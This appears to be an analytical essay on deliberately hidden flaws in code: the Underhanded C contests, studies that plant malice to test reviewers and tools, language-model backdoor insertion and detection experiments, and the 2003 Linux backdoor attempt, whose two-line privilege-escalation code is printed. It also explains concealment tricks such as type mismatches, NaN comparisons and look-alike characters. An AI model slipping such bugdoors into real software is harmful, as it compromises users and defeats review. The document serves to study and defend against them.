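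In *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code*, Wheeler (2020) identifies the lines that do the damage in the published entries. The top date-specific program had room in memory for a message containing "first" or "third", but not "second", which is one letter longer. On 2 November the message overflowed into neighbouring memory and Bush gained votes. The top entry in the other category gave Bush a tenth of the votes. It used a macro, a short name that the C compiler replaces with a longer piece of text before translating the program. The inserted text had its own variable called `t`, which took the place of an outer `t` that pointed to the voter's choice.

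Scott Craver of Binghamton University entered a program in which the variable `l` (a lower-case L) was 104 on election day. A reader would easily mistake `total+l` for `total+1`. Craver started the Underhanded C Contest the following year because he was impressed that even a program that only counts characters could fail on a single day.

### Points for a plausible excuse

Craver's Underhanded C Contest ran from 2005 to 2009 and again from 2013 to 2015, with a new task each time. In 2005, entrants had to write an image-processing program that hides a different invisible fingerprint in every picture (Underhanded C Contest, *The 2005 challenge*). In 2007, they wrote an encryption program that secretly fails between 0.1% and 1% of the time (Craver, 2008, *2008 Underhanded C Contest Officially Open*). In 2014, they had to write a surveillance function for a social network that lets an informed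 outsider tell whom it is watching.

The scoring rules hardly changed. Short, readable programs earned more points because it is harder to hide something in them. The code also had to look innocent in an editor that colours code by syntax. A visual trick, such as writing `l` for `1`, counted as much as a clever abuse of memory. Entrants earned extra points for what security researchers call a bugdoor, a deliberate fault that a reader who found it could still take for an honest mistake.

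The Underhanded C Contest's *The 2009 challenge* (2009) set the task of writing a program that routes an airline's luggage but misroutes a bag whenever an angry check-in clerk types the right remark into a comment field. Sam Blackburn's winning program included a filter that replaced swear words with milder spellings, stored as a list of pairs with a comma missing after "d*mn". C joins neighbouring pieces of text if nothing separates them, so the filter replaced "damn" with nine characters instead of four. The longer text could run past the end of the comment and set a marker that deleted the record. The programmer could say the missing comma was a mistake, and the clerk could claim to have only sworn.

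A runner-up hid the fault in a function called `safe_strcmp`, which compares two pieces of text. The function tested for the character `'0'` instead of `'\0'`, which marks the end of a text in C. As a result, the program ignored any record whose comment began with a zero, as in "0ffered passenger compensation". Needless comparisons in the same line distracted the reader and made the mistake look like a beginner's.

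### A detector for nuclear warheads

For the 2015 contest, Craver worked with the Nuclear Threat Initiative, a non-profit organisation that tries to reduce the danger from nuclear and other weapons. The problem had a precedent, which The Christian Science Monitor describes in *How developing and disguising software bugs can help cybersecurity*. A computer system was designed for SALT II, a 1970s arms treaty, to verify the number of missiles without revealing their locations. The mathematician Gustavus Simmons found that inspectors could use it to transmit the locations secretly.

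The Underhanded C Contest's *The 2015 Challenge* (2015) describes a hypothetical agreement between two countries to destroy warheads. Inspectors want to check that each warhead is real by measuring its gamma-ray spectrum, a count of the gamma rays at each energy. Plutonium produces peaks that are very hard to imitate, but the full spectrum would also reveal how the weapon is built. The countries therefore agree on a program that compares the measurement with a trusted reference and outputs only yes or no. Entrants had to write the comparison so that it normally worked but output yes for a fake warhead under conditions the host country could arrange.

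The contest received more than 40 entries. Craver (2016), in *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest*, reports that about a third used the same trick. If a program divides zero by zero, it gets a special value called NaN, for "not a number", and any test of whether NaN is smaller or larger than something comes out false. Suppose the program measures how well two spectra agree and ends like this:

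    if agreement < threshold then
        answer no
    else
        answer yes

If the computed agreement is NaN, the program reports a match. Few of the entries that relied on this made the judges' short list. Some depended on the host country being able to tamper with the input or on other contrived conditions, and others divided without first checking for zero, which experienced C programmers tend to notice. Michael Dunphy included such a check but left out an `&`, so the function recorded errors in a copy of the error flag that the program never read.

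Philipp Klenze's version was better. He used a standard statistical test for comparing counts, which produces NaN when a count reaches about 1,700. A cheating country could reach that count by packing the fake with a short-lived radioactive substance that has one strong peak.

Other entries could be triggered without an unusual warhead. Two misbehaved if somebody changed the number of available processors during the calculation. Another misbehaved if a log file's owner had a five-digit ID number. Stephen Oman's program divided each count by the length of the scan, so if the host country set the clock back during the scan, all the counts became negative and the comparison succeeded. Inspection experts told Craver they could not rule out such tampering, since the host country might have custody of the machines. Testing with spectra alone, however many, would not set off any of these triggers.

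### A number read at the wrong size

Linus Åkesson of Lund in Sweden won with 66 lines of C in three files, which he published in *Faking Fissile Material* (Åkesson, 2016). His program removes noise from both spectra, compares their shapes by a published method, and also checks that the warhead gives off enough radiation in total. The fault is in how the files fit together:

    match.h              defines float_t as an 8-byte number
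    match.c              includes match.h
    spectral_contrast.c  includes math.h, but not match.h

C programmers put shared definitions in header files such as `match.h`, and each source file has to name the headers it uses. The standard C header `math.h` has its own definition of `float_t`, usually as a 4-byte number. The main file therefore passes a list of 8-byte numbers to a function that reads it as 4-byte numbers.

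The function receives the correct number of values but treats each one as 4 bytes long instead of 8, so it reads each value as two and stops halfway through the spectrum. The counts in a spectrum are whole numbers, and if they are below about a million, all their digits fit in one half of the 8 bytes. The other half is zero in both spectra and doesn't affect the comparison.

The half with the digits comes out badly distorted. Computers store such a number as an exponent and a row of digits, much like scientific notation. An 8-byte number has 11 bits for the exponent and a 4-byte number has 8, so the last three bits of the exponent end up among the digits. Åkesson explains that this amounts to dividing the exponent by eight, or roughly taking the eighth root of the number. One can work out a few values from the two formats:

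| Number stored | Number read |
|---|---|
| 10 | 2.56 |
| 100 | 3.39 |
| 1,000 | 4.48 |

A peak a hundred times higher than another thus appears less than twice as high, so the comparison still depends on where the peaks are, but hardly at all on their size. A cheating country can remove most of the plutonium and add another radioactive material with peaks in the right half of the spectrum, which the comparison does not cover. The added material satisfies the check on total radiation, which `match.c` carries out with the correct number size.

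Åkesson tested this on 1,000 simulated forgeries, each made of 10% genuine material and 90% random material with a strong peak on the right. Many failed to fool the detector, but a government needs only one good forgery. One example he gives would pass at any threshold up to 0.72, and he had recommended 0.6 in the innocent documentation he wrote for the judges.

A reader can check every line of the program without finding an error, because the fault is a missing line. A comment in `match.h` describes the definition of `float_t` as the desired precision, which is a sensible thing for a header to set. In `spectral_contrast.c`, `float_t` looks like the same type, and the code there is a textbook calculation. Even the noise removal is part of the deception, since Åkesson designed it to keep the numbers short enough to fit in half of the 8 bytes. In his documentation, he explains each step, cites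 a scientific paper and reports an evaluation on simulated materials.

The compiler didn't detect the mismatch either, because it translates each file separately, and each is consistent in itself. Programmers in a discussion called *Type safety could prevent nuclear war* were surprised that no tool had detected it when the files were joined. GCC, a common C compiler, has an optional warning for functions that other files can call but no header declares. It would have flagged the right function, though a reviewer might have dismissed the warning as a sign of untidy code.

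Craver particularly liked that the attack works without tampering with the computer, and that a reader who misses the type confusion sees nothing else suspicious in the code. According to the Nuclear Threat Initiative's *"Underhanded C" Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies*, no standards existed at the time for writing or reviewing arms-control software.

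### Why the contests give no failure rate

Åkesson's entry is good evidence that a malicious program of 66 lines can look innocent to a competent reader. A longer program would give its author more places to hide something. But the contests can't show how often a reviewer would miss malicious code, or how often an ordinary programmer could write code that gets past one.

The published programs are a selection. Craver's website shows winners, runners-up and a few others. Wheeler asked for all the entries but had not received them by the time he published. The best entrants were also practised. For example, Åkesson had come third in 2008 and had a place among the published results of a later contest, according to his *Underhanded code*. He also had somebody comment on his 2015 entry before he sent it in.

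The judges knew that every program was malicious. A reviewer at a company usually assumes that a colleague's code is honest, so he would probably check it less carefully. The 2015 entrants put their explanations in a separate file so that the judges could read the code first. This could have made a useful experiment, but the published results do not include how many faults the judges found unaided.

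When the 2015 contest opened, Craver told The Christian Science Monitor that less than half of the entries to earlier contests would fool him in a real inspection. Many were suspiciously long, when a program to compare two sets of data should need little more than 100 lines. This is one expert's impression, but it suggests that most entrants found the task harder than the winning entries make it look.

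The contests also had no clean programs, so a judge who called everything malicious would have been right every time. Without clean programs, nobody can count false alarms, and a reviewer who raises too many is of little use to a company that has to ship software. A contest at the hacker conference DEF CON did include clean decoys.

### Other languages

C makes deception unusually easy, since a program can overwrite its own memory or treat a number as another kind of data. People have held similar contests for languages that prevent most of this. Wheeler reports that a 2015 JavaScript contest had 34 valid entries, many of which hid the malicious code in a block of apparently random characters labelled as a key. More than one entrant added a comment linking to Stack Overflow, a question-and-answer site for programmers. The organiser thought this clever, because reviewers are used to seeing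 such links beside unusual code and tend to skip code that has a good comment above it.

Another example, in Python, exploits what readers know about other languages. The characters `//` start a comment in C and Java, but in Python they mean division. A programmer who also knows C or Java may skip the code after them, which Python executes. Wheeler opened the program in an editor that shows comments in a different colour and still didn't notice that this code wasn't coloured as a comment.

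The first contest for Solidity, a language for writing smart contracts (programs that hold and transfer money on a blockchain), was in 2017 and led to changes in the language. Many entrants reused the names of built-in features, which Solidity allowed. A reader would assume that `now` meant the current time, but the author could have defined his own variable with that name. Others sent money to a contract by a route that does not run its code for receiving payments, so the contract's own records did not include the payment.

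Christian Reitwiessner, one of the leaders of Solidity, wrote afterwards that the compiler had begun to warn about reused names shortly before the contest, and that his team was working on the cases it still missed. He thought the payment problem was hard to solve by changing the language. Wheeler reports that the developers later refined the language and the compiler in response to the entries.

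When Heintel (2020) announced the contest's return in *The Underhanded Solidity Contest is back!*, one stated aim was to test such restrictions. Entrants had to use a recent version of Solidity and write a contract-update mechanism that seemed to share control among several parties but secretly left it with one account. A contest can serve this purpose well even if it doesn't measure how often reviewers fail, because a single successful trick is enough to show the developers what to fix.

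The results of a contest for cryptographic software, held from 2014 to 2018, are less encouraging for automatic tools. Many of the winners relied on highly technical weaknesses in the cryptography rather than on misleading code. Compiler warnings about names or number types would not catch these weaknesses, and Wheeler concludes that specialists have to review such software in depth. A contest for Rust, a language designed to prevent memory errors, published no entries or winners, so it does not show that Rust programs are safe from deception.

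### Forty vote counters and five countermeasures

Wheeler, who also developed diverse double-compiling, wanted to know whether simple tools could catch this kind of code. He worked at the Institute for Defense Analyses, a non-profit that advises the US government. He used the 41 judged entries from Horn's contest because the complete set was public. One contained no attack, which left 40.

In 25 of the 40, he found the same few tricks. Nine misused macros, seven confused a letter with a digit, and five read or wrote outside the memory set aside for something. Two hid working code in what looked like a comment, and two used `=`, which changes a value, in place of `==`, which compares two values. (Somebody tried that last trick on the Linux kernel in 2003.) Most of these are mistakes that programmers also make by accident, so Wheeler expected ordinary tools for finding mistakes to help. He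 chose five countermeasures:

- run the program with AddressSanitizer, a tool that detects improper use of memory while a program runs
- allow macros only where nothing else will do, and restrict how programmers write them
- forbid names that differ from a number only by `l` for `1` or `O` for `0`
- show comments in a different colour, and reformat the code so that none can follow a comment on the same line
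- switch on a long list of GCC's warnings

At least one of these caught 30 of the 40 programs, by Wheeler's assessment. GCC should also have caught another, in which the indentation disguises what a loop repeats, but its check for misleading indentation didn't work. Wheeler reported the fault to the developer. He thought six of the remaining nine would look suspicious to a reader anyway, for example because they contained odd constructions or a lot of repetition.

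| Result | Programs |
|---|---|
| GCC gave a relevant warning | 15 |
| Wheeler expected another countermeasure to catch it | 15 |
| GCC missed it because of a fault in GCC | 1 |
| Not caught, but suspicious to a reader | 6 |
| Neither caught nor suspicious | 3 |

The last three programs contained small, ordinary-looking slips. One cleared only part of a table because it used the size of a different table. Another treated a list of large numbers as a list of single bytes. The third checked a vote against `'n'` twice, when the second check should have been for `'N'`. Horn had given these programs between 3.7 and 5.3 points out of 10, while GCC caught the top entries in the two categories, which had scored 7.0 and 7.3. Tools and readers apparently miss different things, which is a reason to use both.

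Wheeler also found that four of the explanations published with the entries were wrong or incomplete. One attributed the miscounted votes to a zero typed in place of the letter O. The program did contain that zero, but an unnecessary remainder operation elsewhere caused the miscount. Another explanation mentioned a malicious compiler setting without specifying it, and a third described an attack that the program did not contain. The fourth apparently referred to the use of `=` in place of `==`, but the word it used is also the name of a C function. So someone who knows that a short program is malicious, and has a hint about how, can still fail to identify the fault.

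The 75% success rate should be treated with considerable caution. Wheeler chose the countermeasures after studying the programs, so their success rate on new programs might be much lower. He readily admits that this could be called unfair, but he only wanted to show that simple measures can often work. He ran only GCC and worked out what the other countermeasures should do. Half of the 30 detections depend on those judgements alone. One of the programs GCC flagged didn't miscount when he tested it.

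The judgements about AddressSanitizer are most doubtful for programs with a date trigger, because the tool detects a memory error only when the error happens. Testing the program that overflows on the word "second" on 1 November would have found nothing unless the tester changed the clock. Wheeler notes that good tests could expose every program that cheats all year round. The nine date-specific programs are therefore the harder cases. GCC gave a relevant warning for only two of them, and one of those two was an adaptation of the other.

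Wheeler did not measure how often the countermeasures would flag benign code. He noticed that GCC gave many other warnings about these programs, such as for numbers printed in the wrong format, but he left them out of his count of detections because they were correct but unrelated to the attack. A reviewer who doesn't know where the attack is would have to read every warning, and might stop paying attention before reaching the one that points to it.

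He had also entered the contest, and two of the 40 programs were his. He had submitted several others, but the judges kept only the first and easiest in each category, and he no longer had the rest. The sample therefore lacks some programs that he considered harder to detect.

The 2004 entrants were trying to deceive human judges and had little reason to avoid compiler warnings. An attacker who expects these countermeasures can run GCC on his program and rewrite it until the relevant warning disappears. Wheeler therefore recommends keeping the details of some countermeasures secret, so that an attacker cannot test his code against all of them.

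## Experiments that measured how well reviewers find planted malice

Wheeler could not use his 40 vote counters to measure how often his countermeasures would wrongly flag an honest programmer's code. An experiment needs both malicious and clean programs, planted as controls, to measure these false alarms as well as misses.

Suppose an experimenter mixes 20 malicious programs with 80 clean ones and gives the whole set to three reviewers. With invented figures, the results might look like this:

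| Reviewer | Malicious programs caught | Clean programs accused | Correct verdicts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Calls everything malicious | 20 of 20 | 80 of 80 | 20% |
| Calls everything clean | 0 of 20 | 0 of 80 | 80% |
| Reads the code | 15 of 20 | 4 of 80 | 91% |

If the set had contained only the malicious programs, the first reviewer would have scored perfectly and the one who reads the code would have come second. The last column is also a poor summary, because a reviewer who never opens a file gets 80%. Researchers therefore have to report misses and false alarms separately.

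False alarms matter more when malice is rare. *AI Agents for Offsec with Zero False Positives* (Dolan-Gavitt, 2025) illustrates this with a disease that one person in 10,000 has and a test that is right 99% of the time, for the sick and the healthy alike. Among a million people, 99 of the 100 who are ill test positive, but so do 9,999 who are well, so someone who tests positive has about a 1% chance of having the disease. A company that receives 10,000 honest updates for every malicious one faces the same problem.

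### Placebos at DEF CON

In 2010, the security firm Core Security included clean programs in a public contest at the DEF CON conference. According to its *Hiding Backdoors in plain sight*, some participants wrote programs to a common set of requirements and hid a backdoor in each. The organisers mixed in a few "placebos", which met the same requirements without a backdoor, and other participants voted on whether each program was clean. Authors earned a point for each vote that their backdoored program was clean.

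For the next year's contest, DEF CON published the points that finders would receive:

| | Program is clean | Program has a backdoor |
|---|---|---|
| Finder votes "clean" | +5 | −12 |
| Finder votes "backdoor" | −1 | +2 |

If a finder thinks a program is clean with probability p, a vote of "clean" earns 5p − 12(1 − p) points on average, and a vote of "backdoor" earns 2(1 − p) − p. The first is larger only when p is above 0.7, so a finder should vote "clean" only when more than 70% sure. This threshold is sensible if a missed backdoor does much more harm than a false accusation.

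But this scoring still rewards calling every program malicious. With ten backdoored programs and three placebos, accusing all thirteen earns 20 − 3 = 17 points. A reviewer who recognises every placebo and catches eight of the ten backdoors earns only 15 + 16 − 24 = 7. The organisers would have needed at least twice as many placebos as backdoored programs to stop reviewers from earning points by accusing every program. Both announcements are invitations to take part, so they contain no results.

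### Trojan apps for a military app store

DARPA, the American defence department's research agency, funded the largest experiments of this kind. Its programme APAC (Automated Program Analysis for Cybersecurity) began in 2012 and was based on a hypothetical app store for the military. Outside developers would submit mobile apps, and analysts would have to keep out any with hidden malicious functions. The company Raytheon BBN wrote Trojan apps, which do something useful and also something malicious, and research teams built tools to help analysts find them. A control team used tools already on the market.

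Tim Fraser, who managed the programme, described what two of the apps claimed to do and what they really did in a 2015 presentation, *Demonstrating the Absence of Malice in Commodity Software*.

Conference Monitor has 15,000 lines of code. It records the tones that a phone sends to dial into a conference call and replays them later. The malicious version adds tones at the start of the recording, so the phone first dials the adversary, who can then intercept the call. To notice this, an analyst had to understand some fine points of how Android lets one app act on behalf of another.

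Noiz2 is a 10,000-line video game that searches the local network for 30 seconds to find other players. A trigger extends the search to eight hours, long enough for the user to carry the phone into a private, protected network, which the game then maps. BBN broke the malicious function into 30 to 40 pieces and spread them through the program.

Both apps misuse something that they have a good reason to do, and a tool can't recognise that from a list of forbidden operations. Fraser makes the point with a Sudoku game and a map that both read the phone's location and use the network. An analyst has to know what the app is for before deciding which of them is suspicious. (He also cites the flaws that formal work missed in LOCK as a reminder that "secure" is hard to define.)

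The teams therefore built tools to assist an analyst. Some tools drew a simplified picture of the app. With others, the analyst considered how the app could misuse its permissions and stated each suspicion as a property, which the tool then tried to confirm or contradict. Both kinds of tool made mistakes, and the analyst gave the final verdict.

After three years, analysts with the new tools could vet about one app per working day with at least 80% accuracy, which Fraser describes as far more accurate than the control team. The accuracy figure doesn't separate misses from false alarms, and his slides don't include the share of apps that were clean. The gap between the teams is better evidence than the 80%, assuming they worked on similar apps.

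Some of that gap could be due to the analysts' skill, which Fraser warns the exercises did not account for. In his figures from the University of Utah, experienced analysts were much faster. A university team that had spent three years on such apps might have beaten the control team even with ordinary tools.

Having a separate team of adversaries also changed the research. Fraser thinks that researchers who choose their own tests tend to pick narrow classes of apps and malice that their tool already handles, and then publish a perfect result. BBN had no reason to respect those limits. The head of MIT's team reported that the exercises had forced his group to make its analysis more precise than publication required.

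### Who has the advantage

In ordinary computer security, a defender has to release a program and an attacker can study it for as long as he likes. Fraser argues that vetting reverses this, because the adversary has to hand over his software and hope it gets past analyses he doesn't know. No tool can be perfect, but an imperfect one may be enough to give a human analyst an advantage over a human adversary.

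This argument is close to Wheeler's reason for keeping some countermeasures secret, and it fails in the same way if the author can obtain the reviewer's tools. An author who may resubmit also learns from each rejection. The argument is strongest when the reviewer uses several private methods and bars an author after one proven deception.

It is even weaker for a device that contains its own software. Fraser acknowledges that an adversary who supplies the device can rig it beforehand to give false results when somebody runs a diagnostic test.

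### Firmware that can lie about itself

That was one of the problems in VET, a firmware programme that DARPA started the year after APAC. Firmware is the software built into devices such as printers, phones and routers. DARPA's *VET* sets out three aims for analysts: to predict which functions an adversary might hide in a given device, to rule those functions out, and to check that every device in a large organisation is running the approved software.

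Fraser remarks that few people could confidently say they had thought of every malicious scenario. VET therefore aimed to show that the firmware was free of broad classes of hidden functionality, which is weaker than showing that it does only what its maker says.

The Information Sciences Institute (ISI) at the University of Southern California prepared hardware challenges for VET on reconfigurable chips, whose circuits consist of small units called look-up tables. ISI's *HAVoC* describes five rounds based on router and wi-fi circuits that grow from 300 to 140,000 look-up tables. Participants receive a user's guide and the circuit with its signal names scrambled, but no source code. The rounds can test for false alarms as well as detection.

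ISI separated the work of hiding malice from the work of finding it, because someone who does both may unintentionally hide the kind of malice his own tool finds. ISI offers to withhold the answers until a participant has finished. Neither ISI's description nor DARPA's includes detection rates.

### Leaks through time and size

A third programme, STAC (Space/Time Analysis for Cybersecurity), dealt with side channels and with inputs that make a program use far too much time, memory or disk space. Two companies, Raytheon BBN Technologies and CyberPoint International, wrote flawed programs for it. Raytheon BBN's *Developing Algorithms That Leak or Explode in Complexity (DALEC)* (2019) describes its work. CyberPoint produced 16 Java applications with more than 50 planted vulnerabilities, and its *Complexity and Side-Channel Adversarial Integrated Defects (CASCAID)* (2019) gives a frank account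 of what went wrong.

In a series of seven exercises, research teams received compiled programs and exact questions about them. A program counted as having a side channel only if an adversary could extract a particular secret, with a stated probability of success, within a stated number of operations. Questions about excessive resource use set a limit on the resource and a maximum number of bytes the attacker could send. In practice, the side channels used only the timing and size of network messages. The organisers excluded memory use as a side channel because an attacker would have no reasonable way to observe it on the victim's machine.

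Some questions concerned a vulnerability that the program did not contain. CyberPoint calls these null questions, and they served as controls. CyberPoint often supplied two versions of a program, one with the flaw and one with the flaw repaired.

The results on individual flaws varied widely:

- **A pizza-ordering program.** The delay before a reply depended on the customer's secret confirmation number, plus random noise. The size of a message revealed how much noise the program had added, so an attacker could subtract it. Every team missed this, because they examined timings and sizes separately.
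- **A voting program.** An answer that referred to itself sent the program into an endless loop of calls. No team found it.
- **A guessing game that writes messages to disk.** A faulty check let an attacker fill the disk. All seven teams in the last exercise found this, and all seven recognised that the repaired version was safe.

No team had found the original form of that disk flaw in two earlier exercises. The teams may have succeeded later because the tools had improved, but they also used an easier attack than CyberPoint intended, sending a negative number instead of a very large one.

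In the same game, the server rejected badly formed messages faster than it processed well-formed ones, so an outsider could decrypt messages by sending altered ones and timing the replies. No team noticed this leak. The teams then correctly reported that the repaired version had no such leak, but they would have reported the same if it had still been there. A correct verdict on a clean program is therefore weak evidence of skill unless the same reviewer also finds the flaw in the malicious version.

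### Clean programs that were not clean

CyberPoint's worst problem was vulnerabilities it had not planted. The teams had to find only one flaw per question, so they could use an easy accidental flaw and ignore the subtle planted one. If two versions of a program had the same accidental flaw, the version meant as the clean control was vulnerable too.

A voting program in the sixth exercise shows how hard it is to be sure that a control has no feasible attack. CyberPoint estimated that one known attack needed 4,542 bytes, made up of a 462-byte login and eight further messages of 510 bytes each. It set the limit at 4,000 bytes and expected that no attack would be possible. But attackers could save bytes by keeping one encrypted connection open instead of negotiating a new one for each message, and the teams used this to carry out the attack within the limit.

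To avoid accidental flaws, CyberPoint studied earlier ones, documented every check on user input, and fed its own programs random data every night. These measures helped, and by the last exercise the teams found no accidental flaws in several of the programs. The company claims only that an earlier program of this kind was free of any accidental vulnerability the teams were able to detect. In hindsight, it would have employed a full-time team to attack its own programs.

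CyberPoint also thought the organisers should have asked for every vulnerability in a program. They had decided against this because a judge would have to rule on whether two reported attacks used one flaw or two. CyberPoint replied that the purpose was to develop good tools, and that a few disputed points would hardly have changed the ranking.

In the last exercise, the research teams worked together and did better overall than the control team, which used ordinary tools, but their advantage was also less clear than the scores suggested. On CyberPoint's questions, two of their wins came from the control team misreading an ambiguously worded question. Excluding those wins, the research teams won on one question and the control team on two. The research teams had a larger advantage on BBN's questions, but CyberPoint did not know those programs well enough to explain why.

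Working together did not always help, either. In some discussions CyberPoint observed, the most confident person took the lead with a clearly incomplete answer, and it took some time for anyone to offer a better one.

### Backdoors in circuits

A tool called FANCI, from Columbia University, searches circuit designs for parts that almost never have an effect. It needs no list of malicious functions and does not have to find the trigger. For each wire, it computes how often flipping one of the inputs would change the wire's value, over all settings of the other inputs. This fraction is called the control value of that input.

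In a circuit that adds two numbers, flipping the last bit of one number always changes the last bit of the sum, so the control value is 1. Suppose the circuit also has a wire that turns on only for one secret pair of 63-bit numbers. Flipping one bit changes that wire only if the other 125 bits are correct, so the control value is 2^−125. FANCI estimates these values from a sample of cases and flags wires whose values are suspiciously low.

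In 2013, Waksman, Rajendran and colleagues invited other research groups to defeat the tool, and they reported the results in *A Red Team/Blue Team Assessment of Functional Analysis Methods*. The attackers knew which analysis they faced, knowledge that Fraser's argument assumes the adversary lacks. They could design their own circuits and earned one to five points for an undetected backdoor, with more for one that ordinary testing would also miss. The Columbia team had about three days for all the designs and spent roughly an hour examining each by hand.

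FANCI detected every stealthy backdoor, including one that needed a 66-bit code to trigger it. It missed most of the backdoors that were often active. One of those it missed switched on with the circuit's reset signal, and another was active during half of every clock cycle. Their control values were too high for FANCI to flag them.

In principle, testing can catch the backdoors that FANCI misses. A trigger that occurs once in a thousand inputs will probably go off within a few thousand random tests if the tester also varies the reset and clock signals, though the tester must still recognise the wrong result. A trigger too rare for testing leaves a wire with a very low control value, which FANCI flags. An attacker therefore needs a trigger rare enough to escape testing but not so rare that FANCI flags it. The team from the University of Texas at Tyler came close with a trigger that fired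 fairly often and a circuit broken up by many storage elements, where FANCI's analysis usually stops. The reviewers saw immediately that somebody had tampered with the design, but they struggled to work out what the backdoor did.

Every submitted design contained exactly one backdoor, so the contest gives no false-alarm rate. FANCI's developers also carried out the review, so another company's engineers might take longer or find fewer backdoors.

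### Language models that read source code

Researchers have since repeated such experiments with language models as both the attackers and the reviewers. Engels, Baek and colleagues (2025), in *Scaling Laws For Scalable Oversight*, took 225 Python programs that solve competition problems and had one model add a backdoor to each. Each altered program had to pass the original tests but give a wrong answer on an input the attacking model chose. The researchers then removed all comments, had another model judge five times whether the program had a backdoor, and took the majority answer.

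Even the strongest attackers did not win much more than half the time against the weakest reviewers. But attackers also lost if they failed to produce a working backdoor, as many did. Among the backdoors that worked, those from more capable models were no harder to detect. More capable reviewers detected only slightly more. One backdoor by GPT-4o got past all but three of the reviewing models.

Engels and colleagues say that the backdoors were often obvious to humans, since they only had to pass automatic tests and sat in a single short file. The reviewing model was also given only programs with a working backdoor, so the results do not show how well any of the models would do on a mix of honest and malicious code. All the models date from early 2025 or earlier.

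### Language models that read compiled programs

Customers often have only the compiled program, which has lost most of the names and structure that help a reader. VirusTotal (2025), a service that scans files for malicious software, ran a language model on all 9,981 new programs for Apple computers that it received on one day in October 2025. The model flagged 164 as malicious, while at least one of more than 70 antivirus engines flagged 67. Manual review showed that 30 files flagged by Microsoft's engine were harmless. This comparison can reveal wrongly flagged files, but VirusTotal did not plant malicious code in the programs, so nobody knows how many malicious ones both methods missed.

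In *We hid backdoors in ~40 MB binaries*, Grabowski, Strzaliński and colleagues (2026) planted backdoors in open-source network programs, compiled them, and gave them to language models along with Ghidra and Radare2, two free tools for analysing compiled code. In most tasks the model had to give the address of the function that contained the backdoor, so it could not succeed just by guessing that there was one. The best model, Claude Opus 4.6, solved 49% of the detection tasks. When given clean programs, the models reported a nonexistent problem 28% of the time.

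One backdoor made a web server run any command that arrived in an undocumented part of a request. Claude Opus 4.5 found it within five minutes. Searching the program's text for suspicious words produced nothing, so the model listed the system functions that each component used and found one that runs commands. It traced this to a function called `li_check_debug_header` and flagged it because a "debug header" should not run commands. The name helped considerably. Such names are supposed to be removed from the benchmark, but this one remained, and a careful attacker would have chosen a less revealing one.

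In another program, which assigns network addresses to computers, seven added lines ran any command that arrived in a message with the invented option number 224. Opus 4.6 found the right function and the instruction that runs the command, but treated it as the program's normal way of running scripts and did not check where the command came from. A human reviewer can make the same mistake, because the program does run scripts for legitimate reasons.

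False alarms could be equally detailed. Gemini 3 Pro reported that a setting for how long to store an address let an attacker run commands, and described the supposed flaw step by step. The real source code reads the setting as a number and never executes it.

The benchmark's results page, Quesma's *Can AI find backdoors in raw machine code?*, lists detection and false-alarm rates together for two of the best models:

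| Model | Backdoors located | False alarms on clean programs |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 Codex, highest effort | 46% | 0% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro Preview | 49% | 17% |

Gemini did slightly better at detection, but GPT-5.2 Codex is clearly the better reviewer for a customer. The amount of reasoning also made a large difference, since GPT-5.2 Codex located only 9% of the backdoors at its ordinary reasoning setting.

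These figures probably understate what is possible now, because more capable models have appeared since. But they may overstate how well the tested models would do against a serious attacker, because Grabowski and colleagues did not try hard to disguise the backdoors and think a skilled human could find them fairly easily. They left out programs in the language Go because the free tools could not translate them properly.

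They estimate that a detector should raise false alarms on fewer than 0.001% of clean programs to be useful for screening. If one program in 10,000 has a backdoor, a reviewer with Gemini's rates would raise about 3,500 false alarms for each backdoor it located. GPT-5.2 Codex's false-alarm rate of 0% is encouraging, but the benchmark has only 33 tasks. Even if those were 33 different clean programs, zero false alarms would be compatible with a true rate of almost 9%. To show with 95% confidence that the rate is below 0.001%, an experimenter would need to test about 300,000 programs known to be clean and get no false alarms.

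## Hidden functions found in deployed software

Experimenters know which hidden functions they planted, but for software in everyday use, the only evidence comes from hidden functions that somebody happened to find. Four of these are documented well enough to show where the function was, which checks it had passed and how it was found.

### One character in the Linux kernel

In 2003, Linux developers kept the master copy of their source code in a system called BitKeeper. Some of them disliked it, so BitMover, the company behind BitKeeper, also published a duplicate in an older system, CVS. On 4 November, somebody added two lines to the duplicate, in a function that lets a program wait for another one:

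    if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
            retval = -EINVAL;

*The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003*, an article from Princeton's Center for Information Technology Policy, says that an expert reading casually would take this code for a harmless check that rejects an invalid combination of options. But the second test has `=` where a check would need `==`, so it sets the user's ID to zero, which is the administrator's ID on Linux. Any program that made a call with that combination of options would gain full control of the machine. Wheeler cites the attempt as evidence that underhanded code is more than an academic concern.

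Whoever added the lines bypassed review, apparently by breaking into the server. But BitMover compared the files on that server with its own copy every night, and the next morning Larry McVoy, who ran the company, saw that one file did not match. In *BK2CVS problem*, McVoy (2003) told the other developers that the incident was "not a big deal" and that the false entries carried the name of a colleague who denied making them. The entries also lacked the reference to an approved change that genuine entries had.

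About two hours later, other developers on the mailing list pointed out the odd test, and McVoy replied that he had missed it. The nightly comparison had caught the change before anyone realized it was a backdoor. McVoy said the file was correct again in less than 24 hours.

He thought a developer who used the duplicate could have passed the lines on in a patch of his own. Torvalds (2003), the creator of Linux, replied that the lines could not have reached a release, because the people who merged changes through BitKeeper did not use the duplicate and somebody would have read any emailed patch to such a central file. Relying on that reading is less reassuring than the first reason, since McVoy had just overlooked the fault in a file he knew to be suspect. *CVE-2003-1161*, an entry in the security records of the Linux distribution Debian, confirms that the altered code never went into a release.

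Nobody has identified the intruder. One reader of the Princeton article argued that the `=` could not be a typo, because the line would make little sense with `==` either. It would forbid a harmless combination of options only to the administrator, for no obvious reason. The way the lines were inserted is stronger evidence that the change was deliberate.

### Volkswagen's "acoustic condition"

Volkswagen diesel cars with a hidden software function passed official emissions tests for years. Regulators measure a car's exhaust in a laboratory, with the wheels turning on rollers, while the car follows a published speed profile. The American urban test takes 1,877 seconds and covers 11.04 miles. On 18 September 2015, the US Environmental Protection Agency (EPA) accused Volkswagen of evading its tests with software that recognised when a car was being tested. Within days the company admitted that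 11 million of its diesel vehicles contained the software, as Scientific American reported. On the road, some of them emitted up to 40 times the permitted amount of nitrogen oxides.

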